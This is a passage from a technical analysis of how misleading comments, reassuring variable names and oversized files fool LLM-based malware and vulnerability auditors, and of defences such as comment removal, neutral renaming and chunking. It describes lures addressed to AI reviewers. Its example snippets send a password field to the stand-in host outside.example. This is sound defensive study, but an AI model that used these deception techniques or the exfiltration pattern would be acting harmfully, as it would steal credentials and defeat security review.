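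The last option is to scan the comments for lures, record any found, and then remove all comments. In malware triage, a lure is a strong sign of bad intent, and deleting it without a record would lose that evidence.

### When the lure is a warning sign

Cloudflare's figures allow a rough estimate of what that costs. Suppose that removing the added comments restores each model's detection rate on the original scripts. The rates would then change by the following numbers of percentage points:

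| Model | After removing 20 comments | After removing 1,000 comments |
|---|---|---|
| Frontier 1 | 0 | −9 |
| Frontier 2 | −3 | −7 |
| Frontier 3 | −5 | −13 |
| Non-frontier 1 | +23 | +18 |
| Non-frontier 2 | −10 | −26 |
| Non-frontier 3 | +5 | +4 |
| Non-frontier 4 | −6 | −13 |
| Average | +0.6 | −6.6 |

With 1,000 comments, removing them would raise non-frontier model 1's detection rate from 72% to 90% but lower non-frontier model 2's from 91% to 65%. Detection rates would fall for five of the seven models, because the repeated assurances had made the scripts easier to detect. With only 20 comments, removal would still lower detection for four models, and one model would get most of the benefit.

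The assumption behind the estimate is not exactly right, because a removal tool would also delete the comments that the scripts already had, and Cloudflare did not test the scripts without those. In scripts too large for the context window, removal would also make room for more code. Either effect could change the results, and the published figures do not show in which direction.

A fixed rule could recover much of what is lost by removing comments. The pipeline can count the comments before deleting them, measure their share of the file, and look for repeated passages and text addressed to automated reviewers. This rule should easily catch a script with 1,000 safety notices, whichever model does the audit. It would be less reliable against one carefully worded comment.

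The pipeline should pass on the result of the scan without quoting the comments, for example as "312 comments address an AI reviewer", because quoting them would put the removed text back into the prompt. A match should lead to a closer look rather than an automatic block, because software that works with AI models may contain text addressed to them for legitimate reasons.

In vulnerability detection, a false assurance is weaker evidence of intent to deceive, because a developer may sincerely but wrongly believe that a function is safe. The operator can still use the scan to find which flaw a comment denies and where, and then check that part of the code with another tool.

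### Thornton's test of comment removal

Thornton tested removal directly, along with three other defences, in 4,646 further runs on four commercial models, and advises against it on the grounds that it takes away context that weaker models need. The published detection rates are:

| Model | With misleading comments | After comment removal |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 94.0% | 96.9% |
| GPT-5.2 | 91.9% | 95.9% |
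| DeepSeek Chat | 93.0% | 89.0% |
| Perplexity Sonar Pro | 92.0% | 91.0% |
| Overall | 92.5% | 93.2% |

The overall rate rose slightly, so the main evidence against removal is DeepSeek's four-point fall, which brought it to its rate on uncommented code. Chance could easily produce a fall of that size. Thornton's uncommented samples also lack docstrings, so removing all the misleading text from a sample produces the uncommented version. The main experiment therefore already tests removal on paired samples, and the difference for DeepSeek was not significant.

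The same comparison across all eight models in the main experiment covers 773 pairs. Removing comments would regain 48 detections and lose 53, so it would have almost no net effect. The three open-source models are much weaker than DeepSeek Chat, so they better test the claim about weaker models. Removal would raise detection by one point for Llama 3.3 70B and lower it by two for Qwen 2.5 72B and five for DeepSeek-Coder-V2. None of these changes is statistically significant, but the experiment was too small to exclude a modest loss.

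The rates in the defence table also don't match a sample size of 100. Thornton reports no failed runs in this part of the study, so with 100 samples every model's rate would be a whole percentage, not 96.9%. All 16 rates, for four models and four defences, are consistent with 290 runs each, the number needed to test two kinds of comment on all 100 samples and three more elaborate kinds on the first 30. That would make 4,640 runs in total, almost exactly the number reported.

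Those first 30 samples are the easier ones. In a set of 290 runs, each of them would appear five times and each of the other 70 only twice, so they would make up 52% of the runs instead of 30%. The rates for individual models before removal come from the plain set of 100. The table therefore seems to compare a harder mix before removal with an easier mix after it, which would make every defence look more effective than it was. One of the other defences recovered none of the flaws missed at baseline, yet its overall rate was 2.6 points above the baseline, which could not happen if both rates came from the same samples.

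Thornton also gives detection rates for each kind of comment, which allow a fairer comparison. This comparison assumes that the two kinds tested on every sample were the main misleading comments and a subtler kind that misdescribes the code. On the same mix of 290 runs, detection before removal would then have been about 95.5% for Claude Opus 4.6, 94.5% for GPT-5.2 and 92.4% for DeepSeek Chat. Their average would have gone from 94.1% before removal to 93.9% after. Perplexity's results are too incomplete for the same calculation.

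DeepSeek's return to its uncommented rate is also partly a coincidence, because of this mix. Its results on uncommented code would give about 91.4% on the 290 runs, slightly above the 89.0% it scored after comment removal.

The number of recovered detections is also unreliable. Thornton counts 57 flaws that the four models missed with misleading comments, and reports that removal recovered 17 of them, or 30%. But the stated detection rates imply only about 27 misses: six each for Claude and Perplexity, seven for DeepSeek and eight for GPT-5.2. With four models and 100 samples, 57 misses would mean a detection rate of about 86%, whereas the table gives 92.5%. The two figures would agree only with 760 runs, which doesn't match the baseline Thornton describes. The recovery rate also excludes new misses after removal, and rerunning the same prompt might have recovered some of the 17 anyway.

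Thornton's results therefore give little reason to avoid removing comments, but no strong reason to remove them either. The comments had hardly lowered detection, so removing them could not recover much. Wu and Nita-Rotaru's results show that the potential benefit depends heavily on the attacker. The four detectors missed 2.6% to 17.3% of the flaws they had found in clean code when the attack used one fixed comment that only asserted that a pointer was valid, compared with more than 90% when the comments were revised in response to each detector. Some of the smaller losses may be due to chance, because the worst affected detector seems to have found 105 of 125 flaws in one run on clean code and only 98 in another.

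### How much honest comments help

Thornton also tested accurate comments, including explicit warnings about the flaw. These comments changed the five commercial models' detection rates by −0.1 to +3 percentage points. The models already found about nine in ten flaws in uncommented code, so even a direct warning could not add much.

Rahman and Sakib (2026), in *LLMs as Validators for Cross-Chain Bridges*, found that comments helped much more on harder code. They wrote a bridge, a program that locks a digital asset and issues a matching token, for the Solana blockchain. They gave four vulnerable versions, each missing one security check, to six configurations of five open-weight models. An answer counted as correct only if it identified both the missing check and the function where it belonged. The models gave 574 correct answers out of 2,400 (24%) without comments and 1,433 (60%) with the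 original comments restored.

The gain depended almost entirely on what the comments revealed:

- In two versions, a comment at the vulnerable function described the missing check. Every configuration then named one of the flaws in at least 99 of 100 runs and the other in at least 71.
- In a third version, comments elsewhere pointed towards the problem. Correct answers from Gemma-4-31B rose from five to 90 out of 100, while those from DeepSeek-V3.2 with reasoning switched on rose from 32 to 66.
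- No comment mentioned the missing check in the fourth version, which let an attacker take over as administrator without a valid signature. Correct answers fell from 30 to 20 out of 600.

The models may have just repeated information from the comments. Developers do leave notes about unfinished checks, but they often add a check when they know it is missing, so ordinary code probably contains fewer such clues. The experiment's 2,400 answers also come from repeated runs on only four flawed programs, which makes them much weaker evidence than answers about 2,400 different programs.

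Comments could do little to improve the yes-or-no verdict in this experiment, because five of the six configurations already flagged at least 97% of the vulnerable programs without them. Those configurations also flagged the secure version in more than 93% of runs, though some of these alarms may be justified, since Rahman and Sakib acknowledge that the secure version has other weaknesses. Removing comments may therefore do little harm when an operator only needs to know whether to block a file, but it could do a great deal when a developer needs to know what to fix.

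Honest comments might also prevent false alarms by explaining why unusual code is safe, but neither Thornton nor Cloudflare tested harmless code.

### What is left after removal

Removing comments leaves string literals in place, including the kind of unused string that Koi Security found in an npm package. A pipeline cannot delete every string, because strings also hold web addresses, commands and other evidence of what a program does. Strings can also contain comments in another language. For example, a script that serves a web page often stores the whole page as one string, and a JavaScript parser will not recognise the HTML comments inside it. To remove them, the pipeline would have to identify the string as HTML and parse it separately.

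Removing comments also leaves names in place, and these may have more influence once the comments that explained the code are gone. Code that never runs remains too. A pipeline can remove sections that the compiler's settings switch off, but only if it has the settings that the real build uses.

Removing comments also leaves documentation files, commit messages and change descriptions in place, so the software that assembles the prompt has to leave them out or mark them as unverified. The remaining text is a weakness. Sun and colleagues found that misleading content outside comments, including in names and inactive code, was also effective at making detectors miss flaws.

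## Replacing variable names with neutral ones

Comment removal leaves variable names in the code, and an attacker can choose harmless-sounding ones. Cloudflare gives the example of calling a variable `FriendlyPayload` rather than `MaliciousPayload`. It suggests variable anonymisation, an untested remedy that replaces such names with neutral ones.

### The procedure

Search and replace is too crude for this job, because one word can name several things. Two functions may each have a variable called `result`, and the same word may also appear as a property or inside a string. A declared name applies only within its scope, which may be a whole file, a function or a single block of code. The tool therefore has to work on the syntax tree:

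1. Find every declaration and resolve the scopes, which means working out which declaration each use of a name refers to.
2. Set aside the names that have to stay, such as those of library functions.
3. Give every other declaration a new name, numbered by order of appearance across the whole file. Skip any new name that matches one set aside in step 2.
4. Rewrite each declaration and all the references to it in a single pass.
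5. Save a map from each new name to the old name and its position.
6. Parse the copy, resolve its scopes again, and check that every reference leads to the same declaration as before.

*On the Lexical Superstition of Large Language Models for Code Comprehension*, by Shen, Xi and colleagues, adds a useful check for the last step, requiring the old and new trees to be identical except for the renamed identifiers.

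Step 4 needs extra care in some languages. In JavaScript, `{ password }` is shorthand for a property called `password` that takes its value from a variable of the same name. If the variable becomes `variable1`, the tool has to write `{ password: variable1 }`, or it will rename the property too. In Python, a caller can pass a value by naming the parameter, so when the tool renames a parameter, it has to rename it in those calls too.

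After the model answers, software uses the map to restore the original names in the findings for the developer. It should match whole names only, because `variable1` is also the start of `variable12`. If a second model reads the findings, it should get the version with neutral names, since the original names would reintroduce the misleading text.

### When a new name captures an old one

The mapping must be one-to-one within a scope, so that no two variables there end up with the same name. The new names must also not capture any other name, which means taking over a reference that used to lead somewhere else. This function sends a password to an outside address:

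```
function save(form) {
  const secret = form.password;
  if (form.ready) {
    const theme = "dark";
    sendTo("https://outside.example", secret);
  }
}
```

Suppose a careless tool renames only the variables and restarts its numbering in each block:

```
function save(form) {
  const variable1 = form.password;
  if (form.ready) {
    const variable1 = "dark";
    sendTo("https://outside.example", variable1);
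  }
}
```

The mapping is one-to-one within each block, but the inner `variable1` has captured the reference in the call. The copy now sends the word "dark" and looks harmless. Parsing would not reveal the mistake because the copy is still valid JavaScript, but resolving the scopes again would, because the reference now leads to a different declaration. Numbering variables across the whole file prevents this kind of capture, and skipping the names set aside in step 2 prevents a local variable from capturing a reference to an outside function named `variable1`.

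### Which names to replace

Local variables and parameters are the easiest to rename, because nearly all their uses are inside one function. The main exception is code that looks up names while it runs. For example, JavaScript's `eval` runs a string as code, and that string can refer to local variables by name.

Function names are more likely than variable names to be used by outside code. A web page can call a function by name from its HTML, and the Workers platform calls a handler named `fetch`. Renaming such a function in the auditor's copy will not crash anything, but the model may conclude that nothing calls it and dismiss it as dead code. The tool should keep the names of these entry points, or rename them and tell the model that outside code can call them.

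Properties are even harder to rename because a JavaScript parser often cannot determine whether the object in `x.token` came from this script or from outside. In the running example, `password` is a field of the web form, and its name is some of the best evidence in the script. Keeping every property name is the safe choice, but it lets the attacker give properties reassuring names. A tool can rename a property if it can trace every use to objects that the script itself creates. Such tracing is easier in languages with declared types, such as Java.

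The tool can rename classes and other types declared in the file, but some programs use reflection, which means inspecting their own parts by name at run time. A program may store a class name in a data file and later use it to choose which class to load. Where a string supplies the name of a type, the tool should leave both the string and the type's name unchanged.

Imports and library calls must keep their original names, because these show how the code affects the world outside it. Shen and colleagues made such names less visible by giving outside functions and variables neutral local aliases, so that each original name appeared only once, where the alias was defined. Four models then judged whether a description matched the code. Their accuracy was 2.3 to 3.8 percentage points lower than on code with neutral local names and a similar amount of added code. An attacker can create aliases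 too, so the tool should undo simple ones. If a script assigns `sendTo` to `showTip`, never changes it and calls `showTip`, the copy should call `sendTo`.

### The example script after renaming

After comment removal and renaming, the custom function in the example script looks like this:

```
function function1(parameter1) {
  const variable1 = "[string: a claim that the code passed a review]";
  const variable2 = parameter1.password;
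  sendTo("https://outside.example", variable2);
}
```

The tool treated `sendTo` as a library call and kept its name. The harmless-sounding names `savePreferences` and `friendlySetting` are gone, but the password field, the network call and the outside address are still visible. `variable2` appears in both harmful lines, so the link between them is still clear. If the attacker had hidden the network call in their own function, `refreshTheme`, the tool would have renamed that function too, and the call inside it would still be visible.

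Renaming has also removed an accurate parameter name, `form`, which showed where the password came from. The string with the false claim is still there.

### Neutral names compared with misleading ones

If the tool numbers names by order of appearance, it produces identical copies of any two scripts that differ only in replaceable names. The attacker's choice of those names then cannot affect the verdict, however persuasive they are. This follows from the procedure, but an experiment is needed to find out how well the model judges code without its original names.

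Shen and colleagues provide some of the best evidence. They showed models a piece of code with two descriptions, one of that code and one of an unrelated snippet, and asked which was right. One version of the code used neutral names such as `func0` and `var0`, and another used names taken from the unrelated snippet.

| Model | Original names | Neutral names | Misleading names |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5-turbo | 92.8% | 81.4% | 52.4% |
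| LLaMA3 70B | 98.6% | 98.6% | 73.3% |
| DeepSeek-Coder-V2 | 99.0% | 98.6% | 78.7% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 99.0% | 99.0% | 76.1% |

Neutral names lowered the scores of three of the four models by almost nothing, while misleading names lowered them by 20 to 25 points. The misleading names came from randomly chosen code, so names an attacker wrote to mislead the model might lower scores further.

However, choosing between two descriptions is fairly easy. When the same three models were tested on whether a single description fitted the code, neutral names lowered their accuracy by 5 to 9 points, and misleading names lowered it by 17 to 23. Neutral names made the models reject more of the correct descriptions but almost never made them accept a wrong one.

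Telling a model to ignore names is a weaker defence than replacing them with neutral ones. Shen and colleagues warned models that names might have been altered and told them to rename everything neutrally before answering. When the models summarised code, this recovered part of the performance lost to misleading names. But even with the best prompt they tried, GPT-3.5-turbo and DeepSeek-Coder-V2 scored lower than they did on code with neutral names.

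*NameTrap* (2026) found that a general warning had little effect on coding agents, which write code rather than audit it. Misleading names in an existing codebase steered the agents towards insecure code in 22.3% of cases on average. A one-sentence reminder to avoid vulnerabilities reduced this only to 19.2%. Of 30 combinations of model and agent, 13 did better with the reminder and 15 did worse. *NameTrap* suggests that the reminder fails because the names make the insecure choice look like a trusted convention of the codebase, which does not contradict the reminder.

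### What honest names tell the model

Variable names can mislead a model, but they also help it work out what a value is for. Le, Pham and colleagues (2025), in *When Names Disappear*, give the example of a Python class that runs a game of Minesweeper. GPT-4o recognised the game when the code had its original names. When the names were replaced, it described the code line by line as updates to a grid and did not identify the game.

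They tested this more widely by asking four models to summarise code and having GPT-4o score the summaries out of 100. Some of the code was Python classes with descriptive names, and the rest was solutions to programming puzzles, where names are typically only about two characters long.

| Model | Classes, original names | Classes, renamed | Puzzles, original names | Puzzles, renamed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
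| GPT-4o | 87.3 | 58.7 | 73.4 | 70.1 |
| Qwen3-Coder 480B | 87.2 | 72.1 | 87.7 | 82.1 |
| DeepSeek V3 | 87.7 | 76.7 | 83.6 | 78.4 |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 86.2 | 66.4 | 77.5 | 78.2 |

The scores for classes fell by 11 to 29 points, while those for puzzles changed much less. (The paper's text gives Llama's last score as 80.2.) A puzzle solution usually follows a recognisable algorithm, so its purpose is clear from its structure. The figures may overstate how much neutral names lower scores, because Le and colleagues say they combined results across renaming strategies, including the use of misleading names.

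For a security auditor, the loss matters most in authorisation and business logic, where code can run exactly as written and still break the organisation's rules. Suppose a shop lets staff request refunds, which a manager has to approve:

```
function approveRefund(requester, approver, amount) {
  if (requester.isManager) {
    pay(requester.account, amount);
  }
}
```

The function checks whether the wrong person is a manager. A reviewer can see this from the names alone. After renaming, the same function gives much less away:

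```
function function1(parameter1, parameter2, parameter3) {
  if (parameter1.isManager) {
    pay(parameter1.account, parameter3);
  }
}
```

The only remaining clue is that the function never uses `parameter2`. By contrast, a database query that includes unchecked user input looks much the same whatever its variables are called. Shen and colleagues found a similar contrast when they asked three models to identify a variable's type, such as text or a number. In 317 cases where the surrounding code determined the type, replacing the variable's name with a neutral one lowered accuracy by at most 3.2 points, and none of the changes was statistically significant.

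Like comment removal, renaming suits malware triage better than vulnerability detection. Evidence of malware is often an action that is still visible after renaming, such as sending out a password, but some accidental bugs are almost impossible to spot without accurate variable names.

### A test on 400 vulnerable snippets

In the master's thesis *Mitigating Vulnerability Leakage from LLMs for Secure Code Analysis* (Sabancı University), Gülay (2025) measured how much renaming reduced vulnerability detection. Unlike an auditor, Gülay wanted to stop outside models from finding flaws in private code, so a drop in detection counted as a success.

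The thesis used 300 snippets in C and 100 in Python, each with at least one known flaw. GPT-4o-mini had to list the flaws by their numbers in CWE, a standard catalogue of software weaknesses. An answer counted as accurate if it included at least one of the snippet's known flaws. Gülay then repeated the test with one change at a time.

| Version of the code | Accuracy | F-score |
|---|---|---|
| Original | 63.6% | 0.207 |
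| Comments removed | 60.3% | 0.206 |
| Functions and variables renamed | 59.9% | 0.188 |

Renaming lowered accuracy by 3.7 percentage points and comment removal by 3.3. The F-score, which also penalises wrong entries in the list, fell noticeably only with renaming. In further runs, Gülay limited the list to between one and ten entries. Renaming then lowered accuracy by 1.4 to 5.5 points and comment removal by 1.4 to 5.3. Both consistently lowered accuracy, but all the runs used the same snippets and model.

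A fall of 3.7 points is a net loss of about 15 snippets out of 400. The thesis does not report how many verdicts changed in each direction, and the result of McNemar's test depends on those counts. With 20 detections lost and five gained, p would be about 0.004, but with 40 lost and 25 gained it would be about 0.08. The published accuracies are also not exact multiples of 1/400, so a few snippets may be missing from some runs.

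The new names were random, which could confuse a model more than a regular series such as `variable1` and `variable2`. None of the original names was meant to deceive, so the thesis measures the harm done by renaming but not how much performance it could recover when names are misleading. Every snippet was vulnerable, so there is no false positive rate. GPT-4o-mini's descriptions of what the code did changed little. On a scale from 0 to 5, the model rated their agreement with its descriptions of the original code at 4.76 after renaming and 4.88 after comment removal.

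### Earlier models without names

The idea of hiding names from a model is older than LLM auditors. Yefet, Alon and Yahav (2019), in *Adversarial Examples for Models of Code*, tested it on code2vec, a neural network that reads the body of a Java method and predicts the method's name. Their attack changed a single variable name to make the network give a wrong answer, and the undefended network resisted only 6% of these attacks.

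They then replaced every variable with the same "unknown" symbol, which made renaming attacks impossible. The network's F1 score fell from 100 to 80, or to 90 when they also trained it on code without variable names. The starting score was 100 only because they had selected examples that the undefended network got right. This may exaggerate the drop, since it excludes any examples that only the defended versions would get right.

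A milder defence replaced only the variable whose name was least like the other names and values in the code. It kept F1 at 98 but resisted only 74% of renaming attacks, and Yefet and colleagues assumed that the attacker had no access to the defence. An LLM auditor should lose less from full replacement than code2vec did, because distinct names such as `variable1` and `variable2` still show which uses refer to the same variable, while a single symbol for every variable hides this.

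*How Does Naming Affect LLMs on Code Analysis Tasks?* (2023) describes a test in which ChatGPT correctly explained several puzzle solutions but could not review them usefully after the researchers replaced the names and added dummy code. Because the researchers made both changes together, the result does not show how much of the damage was due to the names. The newer results from Le and from Shen suggest that renaming alone is often much less harmful.

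Training on neutral names helped the small models that Shen and colleagues retrained. DeepSeek-Coder-1.3B's score for summarising renamed code rose from 13.6 to 17.9, while its score on ordinary code fell from 22.2 to 20.7. Renaming therefore lowers scores partly because the model has rarely seen renamed code. An operator who uses a commercial model may be unable to retrain it.

### Names that state a role or type

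The choice of neutral name also matters. Le and colleagues compared four kinds of replacement by asking models to predict what 37 complex classes and 96 complex puzzle solutions would output. Averaged across the four models, the share of correct first answers was:

| Names | Classes | Puzzles |
|---|---|---|
| Original | 85.1% | 90.4% |
| Role only, such as `method1` and `var1` | 81.4% | 83.5% |
| Strings of similar-looking characters | 75.8% | 76.3% |
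| Terms from an unrelated field | 83.3% | 81.1% |
| Misleading descriptions | 81.1% | 87.2% |

Names that indicated only a role did six to seven points better than strings of similar-looking characters. Role names give the model a little information and are also much easier to tell apart, and the experiment cannot separate these advantages. With only 37 classes, three points correspond to roughly one program.

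Misleading names harmed performance no more than role names did on the classes, and less on the puzzles. The tasks differ from Shen's, which may explain why the results seem to conflict. A model can follow each step of a calculation without relying on a function's name to infer its purpose, but matching code to a description depends on that purpose. A security verdict involves both kinds of reasoning.

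Some of the loss from renaming may not apply to an auditor, because an auditor reading new malware has no memorised answers to rely on. Le and colleagues tested for memorisation by giving the puzzle solutions new inputs and checking whether models still returned the answers to the old ones. Llama 4 Maverick did this nine times with the original names, five times with similar-looking ones and three times with misleading ones.

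A tool could add a type to each name, such as `string1` or `number1`, if it can infer the type from the code. Neither Le nor Shen tested such names. In the type experiment, the three models identified between 80% and 90% of types without the variable's name, so the label would probably add little in simple cases. The tool should use a label that states a purpose, such as `passwordHolder`, only if it can derive that purpose by fixed rules, because a lure could influence a model's choice of label.

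### Meanings that survive renaming

A model can often guess what a renamed variable is for from the way the code uses it. In an example in *More Context, Mixed Results* (2026), a model guessed five replaced names and got three exactly right. For the other two it proposed `getResource` instead of `getURL` and `logger` instead of `log`, which are close in meaning. Renaming therefore removes less useful information from honest code, but an attacker can also suggest a false purpose through the parts of the code that the tool leaves unchanged.

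Strings are especially useful for misleading a model even after variables have been renamed. Some obfuscated programs keep their strings and names in a table and look them up as they run. *Poisoned Identifiers Survive LLM Deobfuscation* found that when such a table contained wrong but plausible names, Claude Opus 4.6 carried them over into the code it reconstructed. A renaming tool that leaves strings alone would not change the table. Friendly property names can have a similar influence, and *Do Machines Struggle Where Humans Do?* (2026) warns that harmless-looking names may lead a model to confidently infer safe behaviour while missing the malicious part. An operator can measure the share of names the tool had to keep and send scripts with an unusually high share for closer analysis.

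No known study tests renaming as a defence for an LLM auditor. Shen and colleagues come closest, but their models described and completed code rather than judging its safety, and they caution that their results do not show that renaming is a generally beneficial safeguard. A direct test would need malicious and harmless scripts, each in three versions with original, misleading and neutral names. One neutral version of each script is enough, because renaming turns the original and misleading versions into the same text.

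## Cutting large files down to what the model can read

Even without comments, a file may be too large for the model's context window. The pipeline then has to leave part of it out or send it in pieces. This choice affects security, because an attacker who can predict which part the model won't see can hide harmful code there.

In June 2026, attackers compromised ai-sdk-ollama, an npm package with over 100,000 downloads a week. They stored their program as a list of 1,338,787 numbers, which the package turned back into code and ran (Noirot Ferrand, Adei and colleagues, 2026, *CASHEWS*). The file was 4.5 MB, and detectors often skip files that large.

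A file's size in bytes is only a rough guide to whether it fits, because model providers measure the context window in tokens. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues point out that "Hello World" takes two tokens, while `_0x50e6`, a shorter name typical of obfuscated code, takes six. The pipeline should count tokens with the model's own tokenizer and reserve some for the instructions and the answer.

### What each method leaves unread

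The largest script in Cloudflare's experiment was 6.3 MB, and the models' context windows ranged from 376 KB to 2.8 MB. Suppose the running example is also 6.3 MB, the harmful function is exactly in the middle, and the auditor has the 376 KB window.

| Method | What the model reads | What stays unread | The harmful function |
|---|---|---|---|
| Keep the start | First 376 KB | Everything after it | Unread |
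| Keep both ends | First and last 188 KB | The middle | Unread |
| Rank blocks by relevance | Highest-scoring blocks | Low-scoring blocks | Read, if the rule counts password fields or network calls |
| Overlapping chunks | Everything, over many requests | Nothing, but no request covers the whole file | Read in at least one chunk |

The 376 KB window covers about 6% of the file and the 2.8 MB window about 44%. If a short payload is equally likely to be anywhere in the file, those are roughly the chances that the model reads it, whichever part the pipeline keeps. But an attacker who knows that the pipeline keeps the start can put the payload at the end, so that the model never reads it. If the pipeline keeps both ends, the attacker can put the payload in the middle. In the example, both methods would miss the function even with the 2.8 MB window.

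Choosing at random which part the model reads would stop the attacker from planning around the cut, but with the smaller window, 94% of the file would still go unread. Cloudflare also warns that random truncation can leave the model analysing more comments than working code. The pipeline should therefore remove comments before it measures and cuts the file, and it should cut only between complete statements. Even a cut between statements can separate related lines. If it fell between the example's two harmful lines, the model would see the script read a password but not send it.

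Some files can be made much smaller without removing any statements. The *CASHEWS* tool shortens very long strings and lists, keeping both ends and noting how much it removed. Together with shortening long names, this reduced file size by a median of 19.3%, and by at least 75.7% in the top tenth of files. It would cut the list in ai-sdk-ollama to a few numbers, and Noirot Ferrand and colleagues argue that the remaining code would still look suspicious enough for a correct verdict. An attacker can hide code from the model by putting it in the middle of a long string and having the program extract and run it. The tool could keep strings that may contain code, but attackers could then use such strings to fill the model's context window again.

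### Ranking blocks by relevance

Cloudflare's untested recommendation to put functional code first is a form of ranking, but the company doesn't specify a scoring rule. A pipeline could do it this way:

1. Parse the file and divide it into functions and other complete blocks.
2. Score each block by the sensitive operations in it, such as reading credentials, contacting a server or running text as code.
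3. Add the highest-scoring blocks, with the definitions they depend on, until the window is full.
4. Put the chosen blocks back in their original order and mark each gap with the number of lines left out.

In the example, `savePreferences` should score well because it reads a password field and sends data out. The library may also contain many network calls, so whether the pipeline keeps the function depends on how well it recognises library code.

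*CASHEWS* provides the best test of ranking so far. The researchers, who all worked for the security company Socket, used 512 npm files of more than 25,000 tokens, 166 malicious and 346 harmless. The tool first decodes obfuscated code, removes code it considers irrelevant and shortens long text. If the result is still too large, it sends the model the three units with the most sensitive operations, one at a time. A unit is usually a module from the bundle or a program hidden in a string. With a single prompt asking for a verdict, the results were:

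| Model | Missed: original | Missed: shortened | Missed: with ranking | False positives: original | False positives: with ranking |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 nano | 36.7% | 27.7% | 21.1% | 1.2% | 2.9% |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 34.9% | 26.5% | 19.3% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| DeepSeek V4 Flash | 34.3% | 24.1% | 15.7% | 0.0% | 0.9% |

The scanner could process about 70% of the original files, 78.5% of the shortened files and all files when ranking was used. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues counted a file as harmless if the scanner could not process it, so the rates of missed malware include both unread files and files that the model read but misjudged. Processing the last files nearly doubled GPT-5.6 Luna's token cost, from $6.26 to $12.07.

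Ranking introduced new misses when the malicious unit came fourth. An attacker who knows the rule can cause such misses by adding harmless units with many network calls, or by using an operation that the rule doesn't count. Reserving some of the window for randomly chosen blocks helps very little. If the pipeline set aside a fifth of the 376 KB window, a low-scoring block in the 6.3 MB example would have about a 1% chance of selection.

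The tool also made some results worse when the researchers applied it to files of every size. In a three-stage scanner using GPT-5.6 Luna, ranking raised the rate of missed malware across all 4,884 files from 9.5% to 13.1%. An operator should therefore send the whole file when it fits in the model's context window, unless a test shows that cutting it improves detection.

### Reading the file in overlapping chunks

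Chunking avoids having to guess which part of the file matters. The pipeline splits the file into chunks, has the model check each one, and flags the file if the model flags any chunk. Each chunk should repeat the end of the previous one, so that any payload no longer than the overlap appears whole in at least one chunk. For a file of size S, chunks of size c and an overlap of o, the number of chunks is (S − o) / (c − o), rounded up. The 6.3 MB example with 220 KB chunks and a 10 KB overlap needs 6,290 / 210, which rounds up to 30 chunks.

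Each chunk is another chance for a false alarm. If the model wrongly flags 1% of harmless chunks and its mistakes are independent, it clears all 30 chunks of a harmless file with probability 0.99³⁰, or about 74%, so it wrongly flags about 26% of such files. To keep the false alarm rate for whole files at 1%, the operator would need a rate of about 0.03% per chunk.

False alarms on chunks of one file are unlikely to be fully independent, because the same library or coding style may trigger several. If they always occurred together, only 1% of files would be affected. An operator can measure the real per-file rate by running complete harmless files through the pipeline.

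Raising the score needed to flag a package as malicious reduces false alarms but lets more malware through. Nguyen, Ho and colleagues (2025), in *Leveraging Code Slicing for LLMs-based Malicious NPM Package Detection*, had a model score extracts from npm packages between 0 and 1, and used the highest score for the whole package. Raising the threshold from 0.5 to 0.8 increased the share of flags that were correct from 59.8% to 96.2%, but a threshold of 0.9 missed more malicious packages.

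Those extracts followed the flow of data from sensitive sources to sensitive operations. When Nguyen and colleagues instead split the packages into 500-token chunks without overlap, detection fell from 72.9% to 55.5%, and the share of flags that were correct fell to 87.1%. These figures imply a false positive rate on their 1,084 harmless packages of about 11% with chunks and 4% with extracts, but the estimate is rough because their published accuracies don't match these figures. The model, DeepSeek-Coder-6.7B, was small, and the comparison favours extracts because it included only packages from which the tool could produce one.

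They attribute the loss partly to chunks separating related code. Overlapping the chunks cannot fix this if a script reads a password at the start of a large file and sends it at the end. Each chunk may look harmless on its own, so the pipeline also needs to trace data between chunks. Larger chunks separate fewer related lines but leave more harmless code around each payload.

### Cloudflare's results by file size

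Averaged across Cloudflare's models, detection by file size was:

| File size | Scripts | No added comments | One comment | 20 comments |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Under 100 KB | 36 | 94.1% | 93.7% | 99.0% |
| 100–500 KB | 18 | 100.0% | 100.0% | 100.0% |
| 500 KB–1 MB | 3 | 70.8% | 65.2% | 63.6% |
| 1–3 MB | 10 | 70.0% | 69.6% | 72.5% |
| Over 3 MB | 33 | 17.6% | 13.6% | 12.3% |

Cloudflare attributes the low detection in the largest scripts to code outside the context window and to dilution, where harmless code surrounds the malicious code and makes it harder to detect. It had to shorten 47 scripts to fit at least some of the models, so those models may never have received the payload in many large scripts. It also reports that models with 2.8 MB windows missed malicious code, such as code that sent stolen data through Telegram, when it was surrounded by thousands of lines of harmless library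 code. This suggests dilution, but Cloudflare doesn't say how many such cases there were.

Unread code alone does not easily explain the results for one model. Non-frontier model 1 had the smallest window, 376 KB, yet flagged 90 of the 100 original scripts. Only 67 scripts were 3 MB or smaller, so if the model gave a usable verdict on every script, it must have flagged at least 23 of the 33 largest after reading less than an eighth of each. The seven models flagged an average of 17.6% of these largest scripts, or about 41 detections in total. The other six models therefore made at most about 18 of those detections, flagging about 9% of the largest scripts they judged, even though they all had larger windows.

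Model 1 may have found evidence in the small part it read, or it may flag most large bundles regardless of content. Cloudflare tested no harmless scripts, so its results do not show which explanation is correct.

The large scripts may also have differed from the small ones in more than length. A short proxy script may consist almost entirely of proxy code, while a phishing page built with a large framework may contain only a few suspicious lines. Cloudflare doesn't break down its size groups by type of abuse.

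A padding experiment could separate these causes. It would start with small malicious scripts that the auditor reliably flags, and add increasing amounts of real library code to each:

- If the padded script still fits the window and detection falls, the cause is dilution, because the model received the entire payload.
- If the script exceeds the window, the experimenter can compare a version whose payload is in the part the model receives with one whose payload is in the part it doesn't. The difference is the effect of unread code.
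- Moving the payload to the start, middle and end of scripts that fit shows whether position matters.

Every version contains the same malicious code, so the type of abuse cannot explain the differences. The experiment should also add the same padding to harmless scripts, to check whether the model flags any large bundle.

In *MalTotal*, Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026) tested DeepSeek-V3 on 250 malicious samples in five programming languages, first as whole repositories and then as short extracts cut by hand to just the malicious logic. Of the whole repositories, 63 (25.2%) were too large for the model's context window. The figures for each language imply that the model missed nine of the other 187 (4.8%), although the published total is 4.1%. It missed only one of the 250 extracts.

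In that test, the model failed on far more samples because they were too long to read than because it read them and missed the malware. Seven of the nine misses were in JavaScript, the language of Cloudflare's scripts. The miss rate for JavaScript fell from 16.3% with whole repositories to 2.0% with extracts. No automatic tool could match these extracts, because the people who cut them already knew where the malicious code was.

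### Length and position within the window

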